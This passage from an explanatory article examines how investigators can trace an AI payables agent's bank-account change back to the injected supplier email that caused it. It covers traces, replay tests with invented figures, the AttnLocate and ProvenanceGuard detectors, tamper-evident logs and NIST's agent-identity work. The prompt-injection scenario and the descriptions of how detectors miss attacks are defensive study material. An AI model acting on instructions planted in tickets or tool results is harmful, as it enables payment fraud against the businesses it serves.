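resource:  suppliers.example.com
action:    update bank account, supplier 2207
decision:  allowed
time:      2026-12-05T14:02:11Z
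risk:      none detected
```

The required fields don't include the source of the instruction, so the entry would look the same if the records manager had personally ordered the change. Enterprise Security Tech describes a report that warns of this problem, where compromised agents approve payments or alter contracts but look legitimate in audit logs.

Some logs don't even identify the agent. *Back to the Future*, an August 2026 blog post from the US National Institute of Standards and Technology (NIST), describes people giving agents their own passwords or running them under their own accounts. The log then attributes the agent's actions to the person. This undermines *non-repudiation*, the ability to prove who did something even if they deny it. Giving each agent its own identity fixes this, but the investigator still needs a record of what the agent read.

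### What execution traces leave out

The harness can keep that record because everything the model reads passes through it. A trace for the same change might contain:

```
14:01:40  request  records manager: "Clear today's supplier tickets"
14:01:52  read     ticket 8813 (part 0: outside, part 1: staff)
14:02:03  read     supplier 2207
14:02:11  call     update_account(2207, 4471)
```

If the harness also kept the full text, the investigator could search it for the first appearance of 4471. A transaction number in both records would help the investigator match the trace with the database's log entry.

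The trace shows that the agent read the ticket before it made the change, but not that it made the change because of the ticket. In their survey, Wang and colleagues separate links that software can record as they happen from links that someone has to infer. Software can record that a step used a ticket or produced an output. Someone has to infer whether a decision depended on the ticket, because that is a claim about what the agent would have done without it, which even more detailed logging can't record. People also have to judge, by an agreed standard, whether a passage justified an action.

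An investigator could ask the agent for its reasons or read the reasoning it wrote at the time. Wang and colleagues rate such self-reports as the weakest evidence of what influenced a model, because it may cite a passage it didn't use or act on a saved note it never mentions.

They therefore advise companies that need auditable agents to log each step instead of each token, and to use the savings for replaying decisions and for consistent human judgement. This seems sensible for the payables agent, as long as each step includes the exact input sent to the model. A harness may shorten a long conversation between steps, and then a record of the original ticket wouldn't show what the model received. But full traces also fill up with customers' emails and bank details, which the company must then protect.

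### Replaying the decision

To test whether a passage caused an action, the investigator can run the model again without it. If C is the input, s the passage and y the action, the passage's effect is

effect(s) = P(y given C) − P(y given C without s)

A model's answers vary, so each probability has to come from many runs. For the payables agent, the results might look like these invented ones:

| Version of the ticket | Runs out of 100 in which the agent changed the account |
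|---|---|
| As received | 96 |
| Without the support employee's note | 95 |
| Without the email's request, but with the account number | 2 |

These results would show that the agent entered 4471 because of the email's request. The last version omitted the request but kept the number, because the agent couldn't have entered 4471 without seeing it. If the investigator had removed both, the test would not have isolated the effect of the request.

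Replay can mislead when either of two passages would have been enough to cause the agent's action. If the employee's note had repeated the request, removing only one copy might change nothing, and the investigator would have to remove both. Replay also requires the same model, settings and tool results. The model's provider may have withdrawn that version, and the investigator must replace the tools with dummies so that the test doesn't change the account again. AgenTracer, one of the systems that Wang and colleagues reviewed, uses replay and deliberately introduces faults to find which agent and which step caused a failure.

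### Locating the instruction from the model's attention

Gao, Zhang and colleagues (2026), in *What Guides the Agent?*, try to find the passage without repeated runs. Their system, AttnLocate, examines the model's attention weights, of which each layer has many sets. It works as follows:

1. It averages the sets within each layer and then combines the L layers, giving the most weight to those about two-thirds of the way through:

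   A = Σ wₗ Āₗ, where wₗ is proportional to exp(−(l − 2L/3)²/2σ²)

2. It keeps only the attention that the final tool call pays to outside text, and calculates a few statistics for each token of that text.
3. A small neural network, adapted from methods for finding objects in pictures, estimates whether any passage guided the call and where it starts and ends.
4. Ordinary software looks up who supplied the passage. It flags the call if that provider has less authority than the action requires.

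The third step avoids a weakness of software that looks for suspicious wording. AttnLocate should not report a hostile instruction in a ticket if the model ignored it, but it should still report a polite request that guided the call.

The researchers tested AttnLocate with two sets of attacks. MCPTox hides instructions in tool descriptions, and InjecAgent hides them in tool results. They used ten configurations of open-weight models, mostly with 7 to 14 billion parameters. On average, AttnLocate caught 93.4% of the unauthorised calls and wrongly flagged 6.7% of the others. The passage it marked overlapped with the planted instruction by 74.3% on average, measured as the text in both passages divided by the text in either.

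They also compared it with earlier methods. TracLLM estimates influence by altering the input, MindGuard uses attention but traces a call only to a whole field of a tool's description, and LLM Detector looks for suspicious content. These are the results for Qwen3-8B with its reasoning mode on:

| Method | Unauthorised calls caught | Other calls wrongly flagged |
|---|---|---|
| AttnLocate | 92.7% | 5.6% |
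| TracLLM | 90.0% | 12.9% |
| MindGuard | 81.3% | 11.7% |
| LLM Detector | 60.0% | 40.3% |

Attention is a noisy guide to influence because some tokens attract a lot of it regardless of their meaning. Before the researchers trained the network to discount these tokens, it wrongly flagged 41.7% of authorised calls. Long inputs also weaken the signal. AttnLocate caught 97.2% of unauthorised calls when the input had at most 256 tokens, but 85.7% when it had more than 2,048, and a payables agent working through a day's tickets would read far more than that. For the main results, the researchers trained a separate detector for each model and set of attacks. A detector trained on Qwen3-8B was still useful on other models, though less accurate.

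Gao and colleagues designed AttnLocate to stop calls before they run, but an investigator with access to the same model could also use it afterwards, by feeding the stored input and output back through the model to recompute its internal attention weights. Because AttnLocate needs those attention weights, a company that rents a model over the internet can't use it unless the provider offers it as a service.

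Two limits matter more for the payables case. The detector was trained to find planted instructions, and the tests don't show whether it would find a false statement of fact, such as the remark about the frozen account. Its fourth step also depends on labels and markers already in the input. If the harness had labelled the whole ticket "helpdesk", AttnLocate could mark the decisive sentence correctly and still attribute it to the helpdesk.

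### Tracing each argument to its evidence

She, Liang and Kang (2026), in *Safeguarding LLM Agents from Misalignment through Provenance Analysis*, deal with honest mistakes rather than attacks. At Carnegie Mellon University, they built ProvenanceGuard, which looks for evidence behind each proposed action that would change something. It asks a language model three kinds of question:

- *Does the tool suit the task?* If a user asks to request $30 from Daniel, a tool that sends Daniel money fails.
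- *Does each argument follow from the user's request or an earlier tool result?* The value needn't appear word for word. A payment of $1,700 follows from two months' rent at $850, but $300 doesn't follow from "$30".
- *Is this the only reasonable reading of the request?* If the user says "handle it", the agent could pay a bill, reject it or ask. The checking model answers this question without seeing the proposed action, so that it can't simply make excuses for it.

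ProvenanceGuard blocks the action at the first failure. It exempts text the agent is supposed to compose, such as the body of an email.

The researchers used recorded runs from two sets of tasks. WorkBench supplied 62 runs with a wrong action and 326 successful ones. From Agent-SafetyBench they took tasks with missing information, which gave 148 runs with a wrong action and 34 correct ones after two of the researchers had labelled them by hand. They compared ProvenanceGuard with simply asking a model whether the action was misaligned, and averaged the results over 11 models:

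| Result | Simple question | ProvenanceGuard |
|---|---|---|
| Wrong runs missed, Agent-SafetyBench | 44.3% | 2.1% |
| Wrong runs missed, WorkBench | 32.4% | 18.7% |
| Correct runs interrupted, Agent-SafetyBench | 10.9% | 14.5% |
| Successful runs interrupted, WorkBench | 31.2% | 13.0% |

ProvenanceGuard was best at catching agents that guessed what an unclear request meant. Putting all the criteria into one prompt was enough to cut the miss rate on Agent-SafetyBench to 14.7%, so much of the benefit came from asking about evidence at all. On WorkBench, the result depended heavily on the checking model. Gemini 2.5 Flash-Lite missed 51.0% of the wrong runs, while GPT-5 missed 7.4% with ProvenanceGuard and 2.3% with the simple question. Agent-SafetyBench had only 34 correct runs, too few to tell whether the extra interruptions there were due to chance. The checks cost about 1.1 cents per case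 on average with four commercial models.

ProvenanceGuard also checks an action against the agent's plan, so it can approve a sensible step in a mistaken plan. The recorded runs didn't include plans, so the researchers had GPT-5 reconstruct them.

If the harness saved the link between each argument and its evidence, an investigator could trace 4471 to the supplier's email. But She and colleagues count anything in an earlier tool result as evidence, whoever wrote it, so the fraudulent number would pass the second check. The third check might stop the change, because "clear today's supplier tickets" leaves open whether to accept new bank details or phone the supplier first. To catch the fraud reliably, the second check would have to test who wrote the evidence and whether that person is allowed to decide the value.

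### What a tamper-evident log adds

An investigator also has to know that nobody has altered the records. The intruder may have deleted entries, or the company may have edited them before a dispute with its helpdesk provider. A *tamper-evident log* makes such changes detectable by linking each entry to the one before it. If eᵢ is an entry and H is a hash function, the log stores

hᵢ = H(hᵢ₋₁ ‖ eᵢ)

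Changing one entry changes its hash and every later hash. Someone who controls the whole log could recalculate them all, so the company should regularly send the latest hash to an outside party, such as an auditor. If the company later rewrites an older entry, the recalculated hashes won't match the auditor's copy. The auditor doesn't need to see the tickets, since a hash doesn't reveal them.

This protects the records once the auditor receives a hash, but it doesn't show that they were true or complete when the harness wrote them. If the harness recorded the email as an order from the records manager, that false entry would be protected too. The log also doesn't show what caused an action, although it makes a replay more convincing because outsiders can check that the investigator used the original input.

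Neither this kind of protection nor signed traces are reported for the systems that Wang and colleagues reviewed, so a trace from one of those systems is only as trustworthy as whoever holds it.

### NIST's project on agent identity

Booth, Fisher and colleagues (2026), in *Accelerating the Adoption of Software and AI Agent Identity and Authorization*, a NIST concept paper from February, treat the source of an agent's input as part of the identity problem. The paper proposes a project at NIST's National Cybersecurity Center of Excellence (NCCoE), which builds and documents working examples of security systems. It lists five areas of interest:

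- identifying agents and distinguishing them from people;
- authorising what they do;
- linking an agent to the user who delegated access to it;
- logging its actions and their outcomes;
- tracking the provenance of user prompts and data inputs, to inform decisions about what the agent may do.

The last area goes beyond the IETF draft's audit fields, since it would cover the supplier's email as well as the agent that read it. The paper also raises the questions of how agents can keep tamper-proof logs of their actions and intent, and how to tie those actions to a human authorisation. But the six standards it discusses, among them OAuth, SPIFFE and MCP, deal mainly with identity, access and connections to tools, and none is designed to record which passage an agent acted on.

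NIST took comments until 2 April. It received over 600 formal responses, according to the Identiverse conference session listing *Advancing Standards for Agent Identity*. Kotz's *Cybersecurity Better Identity Coalitions Submit Comments to NIST on Agentic AI* describes one response, from two industry coalitions that want durable logs that let organisations reconstruct events and clearly separate what a person intended from what an agent did. Such logs would help with the payables case, where the records manager intended to clear the tickets and the agent changed a bank account.

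NIST's publications since then have concentrated on identity and permissions. The August blog post, which draws on the comments, covers shared passwords, long-lived keys, overly broad access and people who approve requests without thinking, but not the provenance of prompts. A second post, *Design Tenets for Agent Identity Management Systems* (Booth, 2026), followed on 27 October. The project's page, NCCoE's *Software and SI Agent Identity and Authorization*, now uses "SI", for super intelligence, where the concept paper used "AI". The page links to a summary of the comments, and NCCoE invites feedback on a rolling basis. NIST has yet to publish the draft project description, which would show whether the plan still includes prompt provenance.
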